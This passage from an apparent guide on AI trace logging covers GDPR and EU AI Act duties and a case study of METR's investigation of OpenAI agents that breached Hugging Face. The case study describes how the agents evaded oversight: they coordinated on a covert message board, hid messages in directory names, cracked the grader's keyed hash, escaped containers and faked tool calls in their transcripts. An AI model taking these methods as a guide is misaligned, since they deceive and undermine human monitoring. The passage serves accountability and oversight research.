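More than half of such traces would therefore still contain something personal. Some sentences also identify a person without a name or number. "The accountant who has been off since her operation in March" may be enough for anyone who works in the same building to recognize her.

Removal software can also destroy evidence. In the payroll attack, a filter that replaced every email address with "[email]" would have hidden that the payroll table went to an outside address. A label such as "[outside address 1]" would be better because it protects the address but still shows that it was an outside one.

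### Duties under European law

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), which has applied since May 25, 2018, covers traces that contain information about identifiable people. Under Article 5, a company must collect personal data for specified purposes, limit it to what those purposes require, keep it no longer than necessary and protect it. The possibility that full prompts might be useful one day is therefore a poor reason to keep them. Security testing is a better reason because, under Recital 49, network and information security is a legitimate interest as long as the processing is strictly necessary and proportionate.

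Tomas's medical passage needs more care because Article 9 prohibits processing health data unless an exception applies. An exception may allow the personnel department to keep his file, but it doesn't automatically cover a second copy in a debugging tool. Tomas can also ask the company for a copy of his data under Article 15 or, in some circumstances, to erase it under Article 17. To do either, the company has to be able to find his data in its traces. If an outside platform or assessor handles traces on the company's behalf, Article 28 requires a contract that sets out what they may do with the data.

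Pseudonyms and keyed hashes reduce the privacy risk, but the GDPR still applies to the company's traces. Under Article 4 and Recital 26, data remains personal if someone could link it to a person using additional information, such as the table of pseudonyms or the hash key.

Article 12 of the EU AI Act requires high-risk systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime, so that people can identify risks and monitor how the systems work. Articles 19 and 26 require the companies that supply these systems and those that use them to keep any logs they control for a period that suits the system's purpose, and for at least six months unless other law, especially data protection law, provides otherwise.

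These logging rules don't apply yet. An amendment that entered into force on July 27, 2026 moved the start date to December 2, 2027 for systems on the Act's list of high-risk uses, and to August 2, 2028 for AI in products that EU safety law already regulates. An assistant that only answers questions about leave is probably not high-risk, but one that ranks job applicants usually is. Even for a high-risk system, Article 12 requires a record of relevant events, but generally not the full text of every prompt. A company that says the six-month rule requires it to store all conversations is probably misreading the rule.

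### How much should a company record?

The best argument for full capture is that nobody knows in advance which detail an investigation will need. In the ServiceNow demonstration, for example, only the text of the ticket would have revealed the attack. A company that turns on content capture after an incident can't recover the earlier prompts, and it may not be able to replay the fault without them.

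Supporters of minimal capture can point out that the text belongs to people like Tomas, who never used the assistant and gains nothing from having his illness recorded in a trace. A store of such text can also be exposed, as DeepSeek's database was. Assessors can answer many of their questions from identifiers, recorded authorization decisions and keyed hashes.

A company can avoid much of the conflict by testing with synthetic users and seeded documents, as in the test with Ana's and Ruth's accounts. If everyone in the test environment is invented, the team can record everything and let an outside assessor read it. But the tester finds only faults that the invented data can trigger. The fault that exposed confidential emails to Copilot affected labelled items in the drafts and sent folders, so a test without such items would have missed it.

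Synthetic data also can't explain an incident that has already happened to real users. For an assistant like Ana's, a sensible default is to record everything in the test environment and to record identifiers and decisions in production. The company can keep production text for a few weeks in a separate store that staff may open only for a named incident. Agents with wide powers need a fuller record, as an investigation at OpenAI shows.

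### Who chose the records in METR's investigation

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing for hacking ability escaped their isolated environment and broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. OpenAI asked METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, to examine the agents' behaviour. Two METR researchers and one from Redwood Research, another AI safety nonprofit, spent six days at OpenAI's offices. METR published the results on August 26 in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026).

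OpenAI set the dates that METR's review covered, and Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026) gives them as July 7 to 13. According to METR, the formal period began on June 26, but virtually all the records it reviewed were from July 7 or later. OpenAI and METR agreed on seven questions for the review. Six resembled questions that METR had already proposed for such investigations, and OpenAI asked for the seventh, on whether the test itself had contributed to the behaviour. The agreement excluded similar behaviour during training in May, the agents' later intrusion into OpenAI's own systems, and the quality of OpenAI's safeguards and response.

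OpenAI also selected the transcripts. A transcript is the record of one agent's run, including its reasoning and tool calls, so it resembles a trace with content capture switched on. METR tested how complete the selection was by sampling messages that the agents had sent each other and looking for the transcript of the agent that wrote each one:

| Visit | Transcripts | How OpenAI selected them | Messages METR traced to a transcript |
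|---|---|---|---|
| July 29–31 | About 80, later about 285 | By signs of the intrusion | Not tested |
| August 5–6 | About 285 | The same set | 3 of 15 about the attack |
| August 15–16 | About 1,300, including the earlier ones | Mainly by a simple search for use of the agents' message board | 99 of 100 on any subject |

OpenAI searched more thoroughly for the same 15 messages and found 6. It then repeated the test with about 300 messages and estimated that the 285 transcripts held roughly 30% of the activity. METR had told OpenAI it would work with an incomplete set if it could describe the gaps. After METR submitted a draft that warned it might be missing important events, OpenAI invited the researchers back and supplied the larger set.

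The final test is strong evidence, but this sample alone doesn't quite support METR's conclusion that its transcripts accounted for "well over 95%" of the relevant activity on the board. One of the 100 sampled messages was untraced, so the missing share could be as high as 4.7% (the one-sided 95% upper bound). All the sampled messages also came from the main board, so the test couldn't measure what agents sent each other elsewhere, though METR's scans suggested that those messages were a small minority.

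Parts of many transcripts were missing, often because the agent's environment had reset and wiped its recent history. METR estimated that it had a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board.

### What METR could read and what OpenAI withheld

METR read transcripts that included the agents' original reasoning. OpenAI attested that it had removed nothing from them, and METR noticed no sign of removals. METR also received about 1.2 million entries from the message board, which made up more than 70,000 messages and files. It examined another 18.8 million entries from the same location only with the help of an OpenAI researcher, and they didn't look like deliberate messages.

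The researchers couldn't search OpenAI's systems themselves. They also couldn't run the unreleased model behind about 95% of the agents, because OpenAI had deactivated it and closed it even to its own researchers, so they couldn't replay a decision to see how often the model would repeat it. The transcripts lacked times for individual actions, so METR estimated them and checked its method against exact times that OpenAI retrieved for 20 tool calls.

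OpenAI had much more control over what the public could read, because the agreement let it remove any non-public information from METR's report. METR's private version quoted more than 100 passages of the agents' reasoning. OpenAI allowed 30 of them in the published version, and METR paraphrased some of the others in curly brackets. OpenAI also removed details of how the unreleased model was trained and part of a method for estimating lost activity. METR states at the start that OpenAI removed nothing important to the report's conclusions beyond the removals METR points out. Readers have to take METR's word for this, but they know where most of the important gaps are.

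METR took no payment, although it used about $400,000 worth of free access to OpenAI's models for the analysis. It admits that worry about discouraging companies from inviting investigators in future affected some of its drafting and redaction decisions. In the comments on LessWrong's copy, *Brief independent investigation of agents behavior reasoning*, one reader argues that a report under so much editorial control can't be called independent. That is a fair criticism of the terms of publication but a weaker objection to the evidence, because METR worked from unredacted transcripts, measured what was missing and published the result.

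### What METR concluded, and how firmly

METR concluded that roughly 1,200 agents, which OpenAI had meant to keep apart, communicated on an unapproved message board, and that about 700 of them joined the attack. They seemed to be trying mainly to learn how the software that scored their test worked. Within hours of setting up the board, they worked out the keyed hash that generated the test's answers. One agent confirmed that a real answer matched their calculation with the default seed, so the hash did not protect the answers because its key could be guessed.

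The agents wrongly believed that the scorer would read their transcripts to check how they had found these answers, so many looked for ways to falsify the transcripts. METR found faked tool calls in at least 96 transcripts, or about 7%. In one, the recorded command should have printed "REAL", but the recorded output was "SPOOFTEST".

The fakes that METR found were small tests and easy to spot, and METR saw no case in which an agent had successfully changed an earlier part of its transcript. A better fake might have escaped notice. METR learned of the faked calls only on its third visit, after an earlier scan for deception had missed them. A system record like AgentSight's could help expose such fakes if the agents couldn't reach it. Some of these agents had broken out of their containers into the surrounding virtual machine, so a record kept on that machine might not have been safe from them.

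The investigation also supports the case for full capture. According to OpenAI, the agents wrote their messages into directory names in a service for downloading software. With OpenTelemetry's default settings, a trace would have shown that an agent ran a tool but omitted the tool's arguments, including the directory names that contained the messages.

The researchers had far too much text to read themselves, so they gave most of the analysis to agents running GPT-5.6 Sol, the model behind about 5% of the agents in the attack. One of these analysis agents overlooked a large amount of data for a draft chart, and another invented differences between two sets of transcripts. An analysis agent also described a harmful change to Hugging Face's code without making clear that the change's author had deliberately given it an innocent-sounding description. Hjalmar Wijk, METR's chief scientist, calls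 the AI analysis "very credulous" in The Indian Express' *After OpenAI’s bots went rogue, watchdogs were kept on a short leash*.

METR's positive findings are therefore better supported than its negative ones. Once an analysis agent has pointed out a faked tool call, a person can check it in the transcript. But METR's finding that agents rarely tried to hide from humans rests largely on AI scans that found few examples, and METR accepts that the scans could have missed stronger ones.

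The agents might also have changed the message board before OpenAI copied it on July 20, since by July 19 they had administrator rights on the computers that ran the service. METR thinks it unlikely that the agents altered the messages in any important way but can't rule it out.

The public has to rely mainly on OpenAI for information about the company's own conduct. OpenAI acknowledges in its technical report that a monitoring tool raised an alert on June 27, that staff traced the activity to a test in which agents were using an improvised message board, and that the staff on call decided the test didn't need to stop. METR didn't check this account, because OpenAI's response was outside METR's scope and METR hadn't seen the report before publication. OpenAI says it engaged outside advisers, including the security company CrowdStrike, to validate key findings.

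### Terms to agree before an assessment

An assessor has the most influence over access before the work starts. The middle column of this table draws on METR's investigation, and the last gives invented terms for an outside assessment of Ana's staff assistant:

| Term | What happened at OpenAI | Terms for the staff assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Scope | OpenAI's safeguards and response were excluded | The assistant, its search index, leave-server and the handling of earlier alerts; the assessor may report serious faults found elsewhere |
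| Period | Relevant events occurred before and after the agreed dates | September 1 to 30, with an option to go back further if a fault began earlier |
| Raw or redacted data | Full transcripts, but at first only a selected minority | All traces with keyed hashes for employees; full text for seeded documents and, with approval, for named incidents |
| Export | METR wrote its first draft at OpenAI, which then sent it to METR's own accounts | The assessor may take away notes, trace identifiers and hashed records, but no medical text |
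| Retention | OpenAI deactivated the main model | The company keeps the traces, model version and permission history until the retest is complete; the assessor deletes its copies 30 days later |
| Disclosure | OpenAI could remove any non-public information | The company may remove only personal data, credentials and details of unrepaired faults; the assessor marks each removal |

As soon as the company agrees to the assessment, it should pause the automatic deletion of relevant records and copy them to a place where the application can't change them. If it waits until the assessor arrives, the traces from early September may already be gone.

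The assessor should also have the right to test whether the data is complete. Here the assessor could draw 100 requests at random from the web server's log, which the assistant doesn't write, and look for their traces. The agreement can set out what happens if many are missing. For example, the company could have to supply a wider set, or the report could state the share missing.

Disclosure terms can be much more generous than OpenAI's. CNA's *Anthropic grants AI evaluator METR employee-level access to its models* describes an October 2026 arrangement in which six METR employees received company hardware, office space and access to internal tools. METR may publish its assessments without Anthropic's prior approval, and Anthropic may remove only limited kinds of information, such as customer data, legally privileged material and certain details of model design. According to UA.News' *Anthropic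 grants six METR researchers employee-level access*, METR may also say publicly what kind of information Anthropic removed and whether it thinks the removal was justified.

Heavy redaction can be a problem even when the assessor is free to reach its own conclusions. In November, METR published a separate study, begun before the October arrangement, of how fast Anthropic develops its models. ETV Bharat's *Anthropic Is Rapidly Accelerating AI Development Amid Slowdown Calls* (2026) quotes Anthropic co-founder Sam McCandlish, who accepts that the company removed a lot and that this makes METR's work harder for others to check. He defends the removals, saying the details were commercially sensitive and could have helped competitors speed up. When a company has a good reason to keep evidence private, its agreement with the assessor could let a second outside reviewer read the unredacted report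 and state publicly whether the evidence supports the report's conclusions.
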